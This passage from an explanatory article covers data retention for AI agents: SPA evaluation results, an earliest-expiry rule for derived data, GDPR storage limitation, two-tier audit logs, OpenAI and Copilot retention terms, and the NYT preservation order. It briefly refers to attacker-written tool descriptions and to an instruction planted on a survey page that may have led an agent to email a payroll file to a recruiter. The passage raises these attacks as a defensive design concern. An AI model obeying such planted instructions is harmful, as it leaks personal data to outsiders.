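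When an earlier request had stored the necessary result, later plans retrieved it 89.9% of the time with label checks and 95.4% without them. Counting results that the agent never stored as failures lowers these figures to 73.4% and 80.1%.

Another SPA mode hides the real tools from the planner, in case an attacker wrote their descriptions. The planner invents the tools it needs, and software then looks for real ones that match. About three-quarters of runs failed at matching, and the agent completed fewer than 15% of tasks.

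### Expiry dates for derived data

SPA's labels cover secrecy and trust but not time. A policy engine could treat a request to store data as an action that needs authorization, just like sending an email. It would have to decide whether the agent may store the data, with which labels, for which later use, and until when. In the case of the payroll agent's notes, the answer might be:

```
store:    salary comparison for the finance director
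labels:   untrusted; readers = clerk, finance director, head of personnel
use:      this year's salary review
until:    30 days from now
```

A colleague who asks for a job advertisement a month later would get no salary figures, because the note was kept for a different use and has expired.

An agent constantly makes new data from old, so it also needs a rule for the expiry of summaries and other derived data. This illustrative rule follows the same logic as the joining rule for readers:

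```
expires(result) = the earliest of:
                  the expiry dates of all the inputs
                  the normal limit of the store that holds the result
```

Suppose a company keeps customer complaints for 30 days. A complaint arrives on day 0, and on day 29 an agent summarises it in a memory store that keeps entries for a year:

```
store's limit only:     29 + 365              = day 394
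with the expiry rule:   earliest of 30 and 394 = day 30
```

Under the rule, the summary lasts one day. Without the rule, it remains for 364 days after the complaint is deleted, although the company may believe that it deletes complaints after a month.

Like reader lists, expiry dates can only get stricter as the agent combines data. An annual report that uses one short-lived record would have to be deleted when that record expires. The company therefore needs a deliberate exception, much like declassification. It might keep the number of complaints per month, which identifies nobody if the numbers are large enough, or proof of a refund for its accounts. Someone should approve the new purpose and set a new expiry date.

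An expiry date also doesn't help if the customer asks for deletion on day 10. For that, the software has to record which results came from the complaint so that it can find and delete them. Searching for the original wording isn't enough, as the copies in A-MEM show. Checking the date whenever an agent loads an entry is a useful second safeguard, because it stops the agent from using expired data if the deletion program runs late.

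### Storage limitation and audit logs

Article 5(1)(e) of the GDPR sets a similar principle for personal data, called storage limitation. An organization may keep data in a form that identifies people for only as long as its purposes require. It may keep the data longer only for archiving in the public interest, research or statistics, with suitable safeguards. The article doesn't set a fixed period, so each organization has to choose one and be able to justify it.

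The principle applies to personal data wherever it is, including in an agent's memory. A summary that names the customer is still personal data after the original complaint has been deleted. The expiry rule is stricter than the GDPR in one respect, since the GDPR would allow the summary to be kept longer if its purpose justified that. But choosing a separate period for every derived item takes work, and inheriting the earliest date is a cautious default.

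Auditing is a reason to keep more data. To investigate the payroll leak, the firm needs to know what the agent read, what it sent and to whom. The GDPR also requires organizations to be able to show that they comply, and the ICO links this accountability to tracing how an agent uses personal information. But an audit log that contains every tool result becomes another copy of the mailbox and the payroll file, and it may be kept longer than either.

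The firm can reduce the conflict by keeping two logs. A long-lived log would record the time, the tool, the labels, the recipient and the policy engine's decision, and a short-lived log would hold the contents. After the short-lived log expired, the firm could still prove that the agent emailed the payroll file to the recruiter, but it could no longer check the survey page for a planted instruction, so it might be unable to tell an attack from a mistake. Investigators need the contents soon after an incident, so the firm has reason to check for suspicious actions before that log expires.

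Even the first log contains personal data, such as the recruiter's address. People can ask an organization to erase their data, but the GDPR makes exceptions for legal duties and legal claims, among others. Whether an exception covers a particular log entry is again a question for a lawyer.

### Retention in ChatGPT, OpenAI's API and Copilot

OpenAI's *How we’re responding to The New York Times’ data demands* (2025) sets out the company's retention terms as of October 2025. They differ between ChatGPT and the API, the service that developers use to build their own agents:

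| Product | Who controls retention | When OpenAI deletes the data, unless it has a legal or security reason to keep it |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT Free, Plus and Pro | The user | Within 30 days after the user deletes the chat |
| ChatGPT Enterprise and Edu | The customer's administrators | Within 30 days after deletion |
| API | The developer, for data that the service stores to keep an application running | After 30 days for inputs and outputs in OpenAI's logs |
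| API with zero data retention | The contract rules out storage | OpenAI never logs the inputs or outputs |

The 30-day period for API logs runs automatically, but the one for a personal ChatGPT account starts only when the user deletes the chat. These terms therefore set no end date for keeping a chat that nobody deletes.

These terms apply only to OpenAI's copies. A company that builds an agent on the API may keep the same text in its own memory store for years, even when OpenAI applies zero data retention. The terms don't specify what happens to a memory that ChatGPT made from a chat if the user later deletes the chat.

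Microsoft 365 Copilot lets users view such memories, remove individual entries or turn the feature off. Microsoft suggests clearing the memory periodically, which leaves expiry to the user. Someone who doesn't remember clicking a "Summarize with AI" button has little reason to check them.

### When a court forbids deletion

A lawsuit can also override a retention rule. The New York Times and other publishers, who are suing OpenAI for copyright infringement, wanted ChatGPT's answers kept as possible evidence. At a hearing in January 2025, the judge refused to order OpenAI to keep everything, but asked whether the company could separate or anonymise the chats that users had asked it to delete.

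On 13 May 2025, Magistrate Judge Ona Wang (2025), in *In re OpenAI, Inc., Copyright Infringement Litigation*, ordered OpenAI to preserve and separate all output logs that it would otherwise delete, because the company hadn't said whether it would do so without an order. The order applied even if a user had requested the deletion or a privacy law might require it. According to the law firm Duane Morris' *New York Federal Court’s OpenAI Discovery Orders Provide Key Insights For Companies*, the court refused days later to reconsider or narrow the order.

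OpenAI said the order affected ChatGPT Free, Plus, Pro and Team, and ordinary API customers. It said the order didn't affect ChatGPT Enterprise or Edu, or customers with zero data retention, whose data OpenAI had never stored.

The parties later agreed to end the duty to keep new data. The U.S. District Court for the Southern District of New York's *Stipulation and Order to Terminate OpenAI’s Ongoing Obligations Under the Preservation Order* (2025), filed on 9 October, set the end date at 26 September 2025, after the duty had lasted about four and a half months. OpenAI still had to keep the data it had already set aside, except data from requests from the European Economic Area, Switzerland or the UK. It also had to keep preserving logs for accounts linked to website domains the publishers had named.

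OpenAI said that it stored the preserved data separately, that only a small legal and security team could reach it, and that it could use the data only to meet legal obligations. An agent's policy engine should make the same distinction between keeping data and using it:

```
agent may use the data:   it has not expired, and the purpose matches
software may delete it:   it has expired, and no legal hold applies
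```

If a court orders the company in the complaint example to preserve its records, the summary stays in storage after day 30. The agent still can't load it to answer a customer, because the legal hold changes only the second condition.
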